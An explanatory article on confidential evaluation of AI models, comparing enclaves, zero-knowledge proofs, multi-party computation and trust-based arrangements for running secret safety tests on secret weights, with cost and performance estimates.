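# Confidential evaluation of AI models: running secret safety tests on secret weights inside secure processors

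## The two secrets in a safety test and the tools that protect them

Confidential evaluation is a method for testing an AI model when the company that built it will not hand it over and the organisation that wrote the test will not show its questions. Both sides send their material, encrypted, to a computer whose processor hides the contents of its memory even from the machine's owner. The computer runs a test both sides agreed on beforehand and sends out only the result they agreed to release. *Piloting the world's first double-blind AI evaluations* (Isaac, Messing and Lum, August 2026) announced a pilot of the method on a Gemini model from Google DeepMind. The pilot's technical report, *Double Blind Evals* (Trask, Messing and colleagues, 2026), uses the name double-blind evaluation for a test in which neither side sees the other's secret.

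### What each side brings

A language model consists mostly of weights, which are numbers, often billions of them, that training has adjusted until the model produces useful text. The developer owns the weights and the inference code, a program it writes to load the weights and compute an answer to each prompt. The evaluator, which may be a government institute, a non-profit or a company, owns the test set, which contains secret prompts and any reference answers. The evaluator also owns the evaluation code, which sends the prompts to the model and scores its answers. The host, often a cloud company, operates the machine.

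Suppose a developer's model has 8 billion parameters, or weights, each stored in 16 bits (two bytes). The weights then take up 16 gigabytes, which fits on a cheap memory stick. The evaluator has 1,000 secret prompts designed to draw dangerous answers out of the model, and code that counts the safe answers. The prompts would fit in an e-mail attachment. Both secrets are easy to copy, and after a leak nobody can be sure that every copy has been erased.

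### Why the developer guards the weights

Bucknall, Trager and Osborne (2025), in *Ensuring mutual privacy is necessary for effective external evaluation*, put the cost of training the most advanced commercial models at tens of millions of dollars. A thief who copies the weights gets the model without paying that cost. The thief can also run it without the developer's filters or monitoring, which is why governments as well as companies treat theft of weights as a matter of misuse and national security.

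The inference code also holds trade secrets, such as the model's internal structure and the procedure for choosing each word. Bucknall and colleagues cite an estimate that improvements in such methods halve the computing power needed for a given level of performance about every eight months, so a rival who learns them saves money. Even with partial access, researchers have worked out one of a commercial model's internal dimensions from the probabilities it assigned to possible next words.

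Trask and colleagues know of no outside evaluator that has received an unencrypted copy of a leading model's weights so that it could keep its benchmark secret. Evaluators usually send their prompts to the developer's servers, where the prompts arrive in plain text.

### Why the evaluator guards the tests

A developer that has seen the questions may train on them, by accident or on purpose. A developer can also game a test if it knows only how the test works. Bucknall and colleagues describe a classifier whose developer knows that the evaluator will measure only the true positive rate, the share of real cases that the classifier catches. The developer can raise that rate by making the classifier flag almost everything. Bucknall and colleagues also draw a comparison with Volkswagen, whose cars contained software that recognised the official emissions test from the steering, speed and air pressure,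 and cut back the emission controls at all other times.

Some prompts are themselves dangerous, because a test of whether a model helps with nerve agents or cyberattacks may contain expert knowledge that the evaluator does not want to spread. For the 2026 pilot, the evaluators drew on a reserve of prompts that no model had ever processed, some of them on chemical, biological and nuclear hazards.

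Developers offer to keep no logs, but evaluators have had no way to check that they keep this promise. When the makers of the ARC-AGI puzzle benchmark tested OpenAI's o3 model through OpenAI's servers, they used only a "semi-private" set of puzzles and held back the fully private one.

Bucknall and colleagues call this a mutual privacy problem. P_D is what the developer wants to keep private, and R_E is what the evaluator requires from the developer. P_E is what the evaluator wants to keep private, and R_D is what the developer requires from the evaluator. The problem exists when P_D ∩ R_E and P_E ∩ R_D are both non-empty. In the example, the evaluator requires answers that only the secret weights can produce. The developer wants assurance that the evaluator is staying within agreed limits. It has no particular need to read the 1,000 prompts, but the obvious way to get that assurance is to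 watch the evaluator at work.

### What leaked questions do to a score

Benchmark contamination occurs when a model's training data contains test questions or close variants of them. *Are Large Language Models Truly Smarter Than Humans?* (2026) lists the common ways this happens. Crawlers collect the files of a public benchmark, or blog posts and teaching materials that repeat its problems with solutions. Collections of questions and answers used in later rounds of training imitate the benchmark. Some practitioners deliberately add the questions to the training data to climb a leaderboard. Trask and colleagues cite a 2024 study by Xu and colleagues that found strong evidence of leaks for roughly half of 31 models.

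Keeping a test secret does not always prevent inflated scores. *Soft Contamination Means Benchmarks Test Shallow Generalization* (2026) examines Olmo 3, a model whose training data is public, and reports that the data contains "semantic duplicates" of benchmark items, texts that set the same task in different words. Training on duplicates of some items can raise accuracy on the rest of that benchmark while leaving scores on related benchmarks mostly unchanged. So an evaluator who writes 1,000 new prompts in a widely used style may get an inflated score even if the prompts never leak.

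Schaeffer, Kazdan and colleagues (2026), in *Test Set Contamination of Generative Evaluations*, measured the effect by contaminating models on purpose. They trained models of five sizes, from 34 million to 344 million parameters, on web text mixed with between 0 and 3,162 copies of the MATH test set, which contains 5,000 competition problems with worked solutions. They held the total amount of text constant for each size, at 20 tokens (word fragments) per parameter, so only the leaked share varied. With 10 copies or fewer, the models scored about as badly as clean ones, which score close to zero at these sizes. At around 100 copies, the score jumped to its maximum. When the researchers reworded the problems, or kept the wording and changed the numbers, scores fell back to the level of the clean models, because the contaminated models had memorised solutions without learning any mathematics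 that the test could detect.

The same experiment measured loss, which falls as a model assigns more probability to the reference solution. For each number of copies, the researchers fitted the curve L = E + C₀ · C^(−α), where C is the computing power used for training and E is the loss that would remain however large C became. E was 3.594 for clean text and 0.0347 with 316 copies. With a single leaked copy, almost all the models had a loss below 3.594, which is lower than any amount of training on clean text could achieve if the curve extends without limit. The reduction in loss from contamination also grew with model size at every level of contamination.

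It is unclear how much of this applies to the 8-billion-parameter model, because it is about 23 times larger than the largest model in the experiment. A hundred copies of MATH make up about 2 percent of that largest model's training text, which looks more like a deliberate act than an accident of web crawling. Extra training on fresh text also weakened the effect. However, Schaeffer and colleagues cite an earlier experiment in which Kocyigit and colleagues leaked translation tests into models of 1 billion and 8 billion parameters and found that the larger models' scores were more inflated.

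The MATH experiment also showed a drawback of secrecy. Schaeffer and colleagues used a public scoring program that at first gave the benchmark's own reference solutions a score of only about 70 percent. Because they could read the program, they found the error and helped correct it. An evaluator that hides its evaluation code loses this kind of help from outside users.

### Choosing the best of many tries

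A developer can also inflate a score without seeing the questions in advance, by testing many versions of a model and publishing only the best result. *The Leaderboard Illusion* (Singh, Nan and colleagues, 2025) studied this practice on Chatbot Arena, a website where users compare two anonymous answers and vote for the better one. The site turns the votes into scores with the Bradley–Terry model, which gives each AI model a strength π and sets the chance that model i beats model j at π_i / (π_i + π_j). The researchers analysed 2 million of these comparisons, covering 243 models from 42 providers between January 2024 and April 2025. They counted 27 private variants from Meta shortly before it released Llama 4 (43 including the site's separate vision leaderboard) and 10 from Google.

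The complaint has a statistical basis. Every measured score depends partly on luck, so the highest of several scores is on average higher than a single score. Suppose the 8-billion-parameter model has an 80 percent chance of answering each of the 1,000 prompts safely. One run will usually score within a percentage point or two of 80 percent, but the best of 27 runs of the unchanged model will average about 82.5 percent.

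Singh and colleagues tested the effect on the real site by entering one model twice under different names. The copies scored 1052 and 1069, with four other models between them. Two different versions of a larger model scored 1059 and 1097, with nine in between. Arena, which runs the site, replied that the identical copies' error margins overlap and that the difference is ordinary noise. That is true, but a developer can exploit that noise by keeping only the higher score.

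The size of the advantage is less certain. Singh and colleagues simulated it and give inconsistent figures, a gain of about 100 points from 10 variants in one place and about 50 points from 20 in another. Arena objected that the spread of scores in the simulation was arbitrary, and estimated a gain of around 11 points after 50 private tests and 3,000 votes, shrinking to zero as new votes arrive. Arena has an interest in a low figure, and several of the critics work for Cohere, which competes on the leaderboard. Arena's defence also depends on a steady supply of new votes, which a fixed set of 1,000 prompts does not have.

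Singh and colleagues also tested how much a model gains from familiarity with a test's style. They fine-tuned a model of 7 billion parameters on three mixtures of data, of which 0, 30 and 70 percent came from the Arena. On 500 Arena-style prompts, its win rate against a fixed opponent rose from 23.5 to 42.7 and then 49.9 percent, while its score on MMLU, a broad multiple-choice exam, fell slightly. Arena points out that an AI judge decided those contests rather than human voters. The result still suggests that a developer can gain a good deal from training on prompts that only resemble the test.

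It can also be unclear which model was tested. Yann LeCun, on leaving his post as Meta's chief AI scientist, said that the Llama 4 results "were fudged a little bit" and that the team had used different models for different benchmarks, according to The Decoder's *You certainly don't tell a researcher like me what to do*. He also said he had done almost no work on Meta's language models since the first Llama, so his account may be second-hand. Arena's April 2026 rules, in *Live and Community-Driven LLM Evaluation*, still let developers test several unreleased variants, but if a variant is later released publicly, its score stays preliminary until it receives enough new votes. A developer that wants a model listed before its public launch must confirm in writing that the model it tested is identical to the one it will release.

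### From encryption to attestation

Confidential evaluation aims to replace a written confirmation, which rests on trust, with something checkable. Encryption scrambles data so that only the holder of a key can read it. It can protect the 16 gigabytes of weights on a disk and as they travel over a network. Neither use protects them during the test, because an ordinary processor needs the data unscrambled in memory, where the host's administrators could copy it. Encryption in use closes this gap by having the processor unscramble data only inside the chip and encrypt whatever it writes to memory.

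A hash is a short fingerprint that a program computes from a file of any size. Changing one bit of the weights changes the hash, and nobody knows a practical way to construct a different file with the same hash. A developer can therefore publish the hash to commit to a particular set of weights without revealing them.

Public-key cryptography uses two linked keys, a private key that the owner keeps secret and a public key that anyone can see. The owner signs messages with the private key, and anyone can check the signatures with the public key. Anyone can also encrypt a message with the public key so that only the holder of the private key can read it.

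An enclave, or trusted execution environment, is a part of a processor whose memory is encrypted and inaccessible to the host. Intel and AMD sell processors that support enclaves. The manufacturer burns secret numbers into each chip, the chip derives a private signing key from them, and the manufacturer publishes a certificate that authenticates the matching public key. The chip creates a new memory encryption key each time an enclave starts and destroys it when the enclave stops. Large models run on graphics processors (GPUs), so the enclave also needs a confidential GPU, such as Nvidia's H100, that can join the enclave and exchange encrypted data with it.

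Attestation lets the two parties check what is running inside the enclave. As the enclave loads its software, the chip computes hashes of the software, called measurements, and signs a report of them with a key that the manufacturer has certified. The developer and the evaluator each compare the measurements with the values they expect before they send anything. A hash alone shows only that some fixed program is running. To learn which program, the parties need a reproducible build, which lets anyone compile the published source code into the identical program and get the same measurement.

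The trusted computing base is all the hardware, firmware and software that could break the protection if it were faulty. Some of it, such as the chip's firmware, is closed to inspection, and researchers have found attacks on enclaves. Information can also escape through a side channel, such as the time a computation takes, the size of the traffic or the power the machine draws.

An enclave protects its contents from the host, but it doesn't stop an inference program inside it from copying the evaluator's prompts and sending them to the developer. The two sides could rule this out if both could read all the code, but each may want to hide part of its own. One remedy is an allow-list, which limits hidden code to a set of operations that can't send data out. To write code for a model or test set they can't see, the parties exchange mock assets, which are made-up versions in the same format as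 the real ones. A release rule sets what leaves the enclave at the end, in what form and to whom. In the example, the output might be one number, the share of safe answers, sent to both sides.

### Four properties to aim at

With these tools a confidential evaluation tries to secure four things:

1. The weights stay secret from the evaluator and the host, and so does any inference code that the developer has chosen to hide.
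2. The test set stays secret from the developer and the host, along with any hidden evaluation code.
3. The computation that ran is the one that both sides approved, on the weights and prompts that they agreed to use.
4. The published result came from that computation.

Trask and colleagues use "privacy" for the secrecy of the weights and the tests. They use "veracity" to mean that a machine's operator cannot pretend to run one program while running another and sending back false results. Even if an enclave runs the right program, someone can still publish a different number in a press release. A signature on the output, made with a key that exists only inside the attested enclave, would expose the substitution. But it would not reveal that a developer had run the 1,000 prompts on 27 variants and published one genuine, signed result. To prevent that, the parties must agree before the first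 run how many runs there will be and that every score counts.

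## Choosing between an enclave and the other ways to keep a test private

Before two parties set up an enclave, they should consider whether a simpler method would work. There are at least seven ways to run the evaluator's 1,000 prompts on the developer's 8-billion-parameter model, and most need no special hardware. The methods differ in who can read the weights and the prompts, what they cost, and how much each side can check for itself.

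One of the seven ways relies on cryptography alone and includes three techniques. A zero-knowledge proof is a file that lets its reader check that a computation ran correctly without seeing the secret numbers that went into it. Homomorphic encryption lets a computer calculate on encrypted data and return an encrypted answer without holding the key. In multi-party computation, two or more computers exchange messages and work on scrambled data to compute a result without revealing their inputs to each other. The table lists the techniques separately because they protect different things.

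| Arrangement | Who can read the weights | Who can read the prompts | Main cost | What the parties can check |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| API access under a no-logging contract | Developer | Both | Ordinary usage fees | Neither the model's identity nor the deletion of the prompts |
| Weights handed to the evaluator | Both | Evaluator | Risk of theft | The evaluator can check everything; the developer takes the score on trust |
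| Trusted third party | Developer and third party | Evaluator and third party | Finding someone both sides accept | Only what the third party reports |
| Evaluators embedded at the developer | Developer, and evaluators under supervision | Usually both | Staff time on both sides | A good deal about the model, but not whether the developer copied the prompts |
| Enclave | Developer | Evaluator | Special hardware and set-up work | Which software ran, if both trust the chip maker |
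| Zero-knowledge proof | Developer | Both | Roughly 70 to 95 times the normal GPU time in a recent system | That the committed model gave the answer |
| Homomorphic encryption | Developer | Evaluator | Heavy computation | Nothing about which model ran, unless the developer adds a proof |
| Multi-party computation | Developer | Evaluator | About 230 times the normal running time in one test | Nothing about which model or prompts went in, unless the parties add proofs |
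| Trusted AI model as intermediary | Developer, the AI model and its host | Evaluator, the AI model and its host | Building a model both sides trust | Very little so far |

### Arrangements that depend on trust

Most outside evaluators send their prompts to the developer's servers through an API. This is cheap and the weights stay where they are, but it exposes the prompts to the developer. *TRUCE* (Rajore, Chandran and colleagues, 2024) cites a survey in which 42 percent of the research papers reviewed may have leaked test data to GPT-3.5 or GPT-4 through APIs and chat windows, for a total of about 4.7 million test items from 263 benchmarks. Those researchers had no guarantee that OpenAI would leave their prompts out of its training data. A no-logging contract provides that guarantee, but the evaluator can't check that the developer is keeping to it.

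If the developer hands over the weights instead, the evaluator can run the secret test on its own machines, study the model's internals and repeat the test as often as it likes. The developer then has to trust the evaluator to guard the weights and report the score honestly. This is clearly the best arrangement when the developer has already published its weights, because they no longer need guarding.

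A trusted third party copies the secret weights and the secret test onto its own machine, runs the test and deletes everything. Bucknall and colleagues consider the obstacle political, because the developer would have to give up some control over the evaluation and both sides would have to accept the third party as unbiased. The third party would also be an attractive target for thieves, since it would hold both secrets.

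Embedded evaluators work inside the developer's company, on its machines and under its rules. They could get what *Expanding External Access to Frontier AI Models for Dangerous Capability Evaluations* (Charnock, Tlaie and colleagues, 2026) calls white-box access, which lets an evaluator examine the model's internal activity and retrain the model to see what it is capable of. The weights would stay on the developer's servers. Embedded evaluators could also read internal test results and ask the staff about them, which no fixed program in an enclave can do.

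Charnock and colleagues list safeguards that other industries use for visitors, such as temporary accounts, escorts, personnel screening, and logs of the files visitors open and the operations they run. All of these protect the developer, but an evaluator who loaded the 1,000 prompts onto a monitored machine would probably leave the developer a complete copy.

A more speculative arrangement uses an AI model as the intermediary. Both sides would show their secrets to a model they trust, which would answer one agreed question and then retain nothing it had read. It might, for example, check whether the developer's hidden inference code copies prompts. It could not replace the test itself, because somebody would still have to run the 8-billion-parameter model on the 1,000 prompts. An AI intermediary can also misread code or follow instructions that one party has hidden in the material they supply.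 Whoever operates the machine can read whatever the model reads, so the parties would probably want to run the intermediary in an enclave anyway.

### What TRUCE built and measured

TRUCE, an open-source platform from Microsoft Research India, lets a model owner and a dataset owner choose among five arrangements according to whom they trust. If the dataset owner trusts the model owner, they can use an API. If the model owner trusts the dataset owner, the dataset owner can run the model, which in TRUCE's version is open-source. If both trust a third party, they can give it the model and the dataset. Otherwise, they can use an enclave or multi-party computation.

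The platform computes accuracy the same way under every option. For prompts x₁ to x_t with correct labels l₁ to l_t, it sets zᵢ to 1 if the model's answer to xᵢ matches lᵢ and to 0 otherwise, and the accuracy is (z₁ + … + z_t) / t. In the running example, t is 1,000 and zᵢ is 1 when the answer is safe. Both owners must agree to a run before it starts. For the enclave, third-party and multi-party options, the platform issues a new certificate for each run, which the machines use to identify each other and encrypt their traffic. When the run ends, the platform posts the result on a public leaderboard.

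In the enclave option, each owner encrypts its material with the enclave's public key. The multi-party option uses EzPC, which Chandran helped develop. Each owner keeps its secret on its own machine, and the two machines exchange messages that look random.

Rajore and colleagues compared running times on Microsoft's cloud, using Nvidia H100 GPUs. Llama2-7B, which is close in size to the example model, took 0.05298 seconds per test item on an ordinary machine and 0.05354 seconds in an enclave, about 1 percent longer. Multi-party computation took 12.269 seconds, roughly 230 times as long. For BERT-Base, a much smaller model, the enclave added about 18 percent. These are averages over ten samples, so the small differences are rough.

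At those speeds, 1,000 short items would take under a minute in the enclave and about three and a half hours with EzPC. Traffic is a bigger problem. To evaluate Llama2-7B on 5,153 items, the two EzPC machines would have to exchange about 199,000 gigabytes, or nearly 39 gigabytes per item. The enclave only has to receive the model and the test once, about 26 gigabytes in all.

Rajore and colleagues call EzPC's overhead "tractable", which seems fair for the test they chose, LAMBADA, in which a model predicts a word and so produces very little output per item. A safety test usually needs whole answers, and a language model produces an answer one token at a time. If each token needed as much time and network traffic as one LAMBADA item, 1,000 answers of 200 tokens each would take about four weeks and 7.7 million gigabytes. Reusing earlier calculations would lower these figures, but they would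 have to fall a long way before an evaluator preferred EzPC for its efficiency.

Multi-party computation also requires some trust between the two sides. Both must know the model's architecture, which a developer may want to hide. The fastest systems, including EzPC, also rely on both sides to run the agreed program faithfully. Slower versions remove this requirement, but a developer could still feed in the wrong model unless it had committed to a particular set of weights and could prove that it used them.

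### What a zero-knowledge proof can show

A zero-knowledge proof addresses a different worry, that the answer may not have come from the promised model. *Verifiable evaluations of machine learning models using zkSNARKs* (South, Camuto and colleagues, 2024) applies such proofs to whole evaluations. It uses zk-SNARKs, a kind of zero-knowledge proof that is short and quick to check.

The developer converts its model into a circuit, a long list of equations that hold only if every step of the calculation is right. A set-up program then produces a large proving key, pk, for the developer and a small verification key for everyone else. For each test item x, the developer runs the model with weights W to get an answer y, and generates a proof π = Prove(pk, W, x, y). The proof reveals y and a hash of the weights, H(W), but not the weights. Anyone can check that every proof carries the same hash and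 then add up the score. The developer can combine the results in a further proof that reveals only the accuracy, but this takes more computation and someone has to audit the scoring code.

South and colleagues tried this on eight small models. The largest language model was a version of nanoGPT with 250,000 parameters. Each of its proofs took 2,781 seconds to generate and 2.69 seconds to check, and the proving key took up 219 gigabytes. Since a language model needs a proof for each token, proving 1,000 one-token answers would have taken about 32 days on a single machine. If proving time grew in proportion to model size, proving one token from the example model, which is 32,000 times larger, would take nearly three years.

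Later systems replaced the general-purpose circuit with methods suited to neural networks. *Infrastructure for Verifiable AI* (Xia, Xu and Wang, 2026) describes one of the most important, the sumcheck protocol. Language models mostly do matrix multiplication, and each entry of the result is a long sum. Sumcheck reduces a claim about a sum of 2ⁿ terms to n short rounds, so a sum of 4,096 terms needs only 12. In each round the verifier sends a random number and the prover must reply with a matching polynomial. A prover that lied about the total will almost certainly fail. For operations that are awkward to write as sums, the prover shows that each input and output pair appears in a table fixed in advance.

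*Towards Verifiable AI with Lightweight Cryptographic Proofs of Inference* (2026) reports that zkLLM, which uses these methods, took 388.3 seconds to prove a run of Llama-2-7B and 2.36 seconds to check the proof. At that rate, proving 1,000 runs would take about four and a half days. Polyhedra (2025), a company that develops proof software, claims a proving time of about 150 seconds per token for Llama-3 8B on a single processor core.

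The largest model of known size with a full zero-knowledge proof seems to be Llama 4 Maverick, which has about 400 billion parameters and uses about 17 billion of them for each token. The proof comes from FlashProve, a prototype that Anthropic built with researchers at EPFL, MIT and StarkWare, according to Help Net Security's *Anthropic open-sources FlashProve, its provable inference prototype for MoE models* (2026). *Zero-Knowledge Proof Based Verifiable Inference of Models* (2025) may cover a larger model, because it presents a provable version of a DeepSeek model and some DeepSeek models are larger than Maverick. *Seal, Then Sample* (2026) reaches 70 billion parameters by proving only a sample of the layers, but that result comes from a single run.

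FlashProve processes about 110 tokens per second on one H100, but by default it proves only about one new token every nine seconds. *Sable* (Solberg, 2026), which describes a competing system, explains that FlashProve works on batches of 24 windows, each 1,024 tokens long. A batch takes about 220 seconds and by default proves only the one token that follows each window, or 24 new tokens in total. *Maverick* (2026), a paper on another rival method that shares the model's name, gives 58.8 seconds for one token after a 1,024-token prompt, presumably without batching. FlashProve can also check every token of a finished reply, but against a looser standard.

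Help Net Security puts the overhead at about 72 times the normal GPU time, or 94 times at the heaviest load. Even so, proving 1,000 windows would take less than three hours on one GPU, which is probably acceptable for an important test.

The restrictions are a bigger obstacle than the price. Infobae's *Anthropic creó un sistema que permite comprobar qué modelo de IA escribió* (2026) reports that FlashProve handles at most 1,024 tokens of context and works only for mixture-of-experts models, which use only part of their network for each token. If the example model uses all 8 billion parameters for each token, FlashProve can't prove its answers. FlashProve hides the weights but not the architecture, and the time taken to generate a proof might reveal information about the weights.

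FlashProve and Sable also run their proofs on a slightly different model from the one the developer trained. Ordinary GPU arithmetic rounds its results, and the rounding depends on details such as the order of additions, so both systems replace it with exact integer arithmetic. Solberg reports that the most likely token differs between FlashProve's version and the original in 6.8 percent of positions on one set of texts and 9.4 percent on another. For Sable's version of Qwen2.5-32B, it differs in 13.7 percent. Benchmark scores can still be close. Sable's versions of two other models scored within 1.6 points of the originals on the MMLU exam. But a safety score for the integer version applies to the public product only to the extent that the two behave alike.

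Sable handles models that use all their parameters for every token. It proves Qwen2.5-32B's computation on 4,096 tokens in 92.5 seconds on one GPU, for about 6.4 cents. However, its proofs are not zero-knowledge, and Solberg estimates that about 20,000 of them would leak the weights. With one proof per prompt, the example test would produce that many proofs in 20 runs.

None of these proofs hides the prompts from the developer. Whoever generates the proof needs both W and x, and since the developer won't share W, the evaluator has to share x. South and colleagues suggest publishing only a hash of a private test set, which would hide the questions from the public but not from the developer.

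Homomorphic encryption would deal with this. The evaluator would encrypt its 1,000 prompts, the developer would run its model on the encrypted text, and only the evaluator could decrypt the answers. *Privacy-Preserving Mechanisms Enable Cheap Verifiable Inference of LLMs* (2026) says that homomorphic encryption and multi-party computation both add "significant overhead" to language models. The evaluator would also need a proof that the developer had used the right weights, which would take a lot of additional computation.

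### Does current practice neglect the evaluator?

Bucknall and colleagues argue that outside evaluation can't work well unless both sides keep their secrets, and that current practice mostly protects the developer. They attribute this partly to bargaining power, since evaluations are voluntary and a developer that dislikes the evaluator's terms can refuse. They also find the same bias in proposals for improvement. South and colleagues assume the developer sees the whole audit, and an earlier design by Trask and colleagues requires the developer to read and approve all the evaluator's code.

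The paper by Charnock and colleagues, published a year later, fits this pattern. The two main challenges they name for companies that widen access, leaks of company secrets and demands on staff, both fall on the developer.

But Bucknall and colleagues overstate the case when they say that cryptographic work on private auditing has focused solely on the developer's security. TRUCE, which came out the year before their paper, aimed to protect the test set. With EzPC, a developer that follows the protocol never receives a readable prompt to log. It would be fairer to say that the tools existed but evaluators rarely got to use them.

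"Essential" also seems too strong. An evaluator that writes new, harmless prompts for each test loses little if the developer keeps them, apart from the work of writing more. Secrecy matters much more if the evaluator wants to reuse the prompts, compare models over several years, or ask about dangerous subjects.

There is also a case for letting the developer watch the tests. After an audit by ARC (now METR), Anthropic said it could have helped the auditors find more worrying behaviour if it had known more about their approach. Bucknall and colleagues reply that developers could give evaluators more information instead, and that independence is worth having even if evaluators must rediscover some things the developer already knows. That argument works for an evaluator with plenty of time, but it is less convincing for one with less than a week, which is what Charnock and colleagues say Apollo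 Research and the UK's AI Security Institute had for Claude Sonnet 4.5.

Another objection is that nobody can judge the quality of a secret test. Bucknall and colleagues suggest that an official body could accredit evaluators. Rajore and colleagues offer a more direct check. The evaluator first commits to every prompt, in effect sealing each one in a locked box. An auditor then picks k boxes at random, and the evaluator opens them for the auditor to check. If at most a share α of the prompts is good, the chance that all k pass is at most about αᵏ. With α = 0.95 and k = 100, that chance is about 0.006. So by reading 100 of the 1,000 prompts, an auditor could be fairly sure that at least 95 percent are good.

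An evaluator could still show the auditor a good test set and run a bad one. To rule this out with multi-party computation, the evaluator would have to supply a zero-knowledge proof that the two sets match. An enclave has an advantage unrelated to speed, because it can simply compare the prompts it receives with the commitments to the audited set.

### What the rules ask for

The European Union's General-Purpose AI Code of Practice asks the companies that sign it to give outside evaluators "appropriate" access to a model, information about it and time to test it. According to Charnock and colleagues, the Code allows "appropriate" to mean best practice, the state of the art or "more innovative processes", but does not specify what any of these involves.

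Charnock and colleagues propose three levels of access to fill the gap. At the lowest, the evaluator can only send prompts and read answers, which they think might be enough for a minor update. The middle level adds some view of the model's internals, such as the probabilities it assigns to possible next words, and substantial information about how the developer built and tested it. The highest level gives white-box access and comprehensive information, for models much more capable than their predecessors. How these levels correspond to the Code is their own interpretation.

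The levels measure how much the evaluator learns about the model, not how much the developer learns about the test, so a developer could reach the highest level and still record every prompt. Charnock and colleagues discuss privacy-preserving tools such as enclaves mainly as a way to make the highest level safe for the developer. They add that these tools need to become more efficient and easier to operate, and note that an earlier enclave trial required all parties to be online at the same time.

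### When an enclave is the better choice

For the 8-billion-parameter model, the choice depends mostly on what each side still needs to keep secret. If the weights are public, the evaluator can download them. If the prompts are harmless and the evaluator can replace them, API access is enough. An enclave is worth the effort when the developer won't release the weights and the evaluator wants to reuse the prompts or can't safely show them to anyone.

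The choice also depends on the kind of test. An enclave works well if the evaluator can write the whole test as a program beforehand and the result is small, such as the share of safe answers. It works poorly for an open-ended investigation, because the evaluator has to see each answer before deciding what to try next. Embedded evaluators are better at that, and they could still use an enclave for the part of their work that depends on secret prompts.

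Both sides must also trust the chip maker. Xia and colleagues consider this the main weakness of enclaves compared with proofs, which anyone can check without trusting a manufacturer. If a regulator or a rival government does not trust the chip maker, a zero-knowledge proof may be the only acceptable evidence about a model with secret weights, but using one would require the evaluator to show the developer the prompts.

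In practice, the choice may depend on how much time the evaluator has. The enclave adds very little running time in TRUCE's measurements, but the parties have to arrange the hardware, agree on the code and rehearse the run before the test starts. If the evaluator has less than a week with a new model, most of that work has to happen before the model is ready.

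## Choosing the processors and estimating size, speed and cost

A confidential test needs a processor that supports enclaves, enough memory to hold the model, and usually a GPU. The 8-billion-parameter model fits on a single GPU. The largest commercial models need several GPUs working together, which narrows the choice of hardware.

### Enclaves for one program or a whole virtual machine

Intel's SGX protects a single program inside an enclave. The operating system stays outside, so neither side has to trust it, but programmers usually have to adapt the program. Intel's TDX and AMD's SEV-SNP protect a whole virtual machine, a simulated computer that has its own operating system and shares the physical machine with others. Ordinary software runs in it unchanged, including the drivers that control a GPU. However, the trusted computing base is larger, because a fault in the protected operating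 system could expose both the tests and the weights. Amazon's Nitro Enclaves also isolate a virtual machine, but they depend on Amazon's hardware and software.

*Evaluating the Performance of the DeepSeek Model in Confidential Computing Environment* (Dong and Wang, 2025) gives SGX's memory limit as about 1 gigabyte, far too little for 16 gigabytes of weights. That figure probably describes older chips, since *Confidential LLM Inference* (2025) reports running Llama 2 models with up to 70 billion parameters in both SGX and TDX.

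With any of these products, a developer who wants to keep inference code secret would load it in two steps. The *Technical Position Paper on Confidential Computing* (2025), from the French cybersecurity agency ANSSI, notes that the processor must receive an enclave's first program unencrypted. The developer would therefore start a small public program, which would then fetch the secret code in encrypted form.

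### Doing without a GPU

A small model can run on the main processor alone. Dong and Wang ran a 7-billion-parameter version of DeepSeek R1 inside TDX at 6.4 tokens per second, compared with 117 on a machine with a GPU and no enclave. At those speeds, if the model wrote one answer at a time, 1,000 answers of 200 tokens each would take about half an hour on the GPU and nearly nine hours in the enclave, which an evaluator could leave running overnight.

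Dong and Wang calculated that the GPU was 12 times as fast on average. But for their 14-billion-parameter model they divided by the speed of an ordinary processor instead of the speed in TDX, and correcting this raises the average to about 15. Encryption accounts for little of the gap, since *Confidential LLM Inference* found that enclaves reduced a processor's throughput, the number of tokens it handles per second, by less than 10 percent. The prototype in *Attestable Audits* (2025) runs on Nitro Enclaves at the slower speed because it doesn't use a GPU.

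### How a GPU joins the enclave

Pattern Labs and Anthropic's *Confidential Inference Systems* (2025) describes two ways to extend an enclave to a GPU. The GPU can have its own encryption and attestation, or the system can attach an unprotected GPU to the processor's enclave. Nvidia takes the first approach. Its GPUs with this protection include the H100 and H200, from the Hopper generation, and the newer B200 and B300, from the Blackwell generation.

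Like the processor, each of these GPUs has a built-in signing key. According to Nvidia's *Hardware-Rooted AI Security That Won't Slow You Down*, the company's attestation service checks the GPU's signed report together with one from TDX or SEV-SNP. The GPU and the enclave then encrypt everything they send each other over PCIe, which connects them inside the computer.

Each of the evaluator's prompts would arrive in the virtual machine's encrypted memory, and the processor would decrypt it and split it into tokens. The GPU can't read the virtual machine's private memory, so the processor would encrypt the tokens again with a key it shares with the GPU and place them in a bounce buffer, an area of memory that both can access. The host can also access this buffer, but would find only encrypted data there. The GPU would then fetch the data over PCIe and decrypt it into its own memory.

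The weights take the same route once, at the start, and then stay in the GPU's memory, which is not encrypted. *The Serialized Bridge* (Yin and Wang, 2026) explains that access controls block the host from reading this memory. The GPU processes the whole prompt at once and then writes the answer one token at a time. After each token, it sends the result back through the bounce buffer, and the processor sends commands for the next one. When the answer is complete, the evaluation code scores it inside the enclave.

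### Where the time goes

The GPU's arithmetic runs at nearly full speed. Yin and Wang measured matrix multiplication on a B300 at 99.8 percent of its normal rate. Almost all the delay comes from traffic between the processor and the GPU, and much of that traffic consists of commands.

Asad and Grunseid (2026), in *Benchmarking Confidential Computing Performance on NVIDIA Blackwell GPUs*, found that sending one command to a B200 GPU took 3.45 microseconds normally and 15.7 in confidential mode. Confidential mode therefore adds about 12 microseconds per command, and a language model may need hundreds of commands for each token. For vLLM, a widely used program for running language models, they counted about 185 commands per step, which predicts an added delay of 2.2 milliseconds per step, close to the 2.28 they measured.

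Software can avoid most of this delay with a CUDA graph, which records a sequence of GPU commands and replays it with a single command. In a synthetic test with 181 commands per step, confidential mode made each step take 2.41 times as long when the processor sent the commands separately, and 1.04 times as long when a CUDA graph replayed the whole sequence.

Another delay comes from waiting for each token to be copied back from the GPU. Normally the processor prepares the next step during the copy, but in confidential mode the copy holds up the program, leaving the GPU idle. Asad and Grunseid measured the effect on Qwen3-8B, which is the same size as the example model and also uses 16 bits per parameter. With an unmodified version of SGLang, another program for running models, throughput on a B200 fell from 11,137 to 6,805 tokens per second, a loss of 39 percent. A patch that moves the waiting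 to a separate worker nearly eliminated the loss on a 72-billion-parameter model, leaving a median loss of 1.2 percent and a maximum of 6.5 percent across ten combinations of prompt and answer length.

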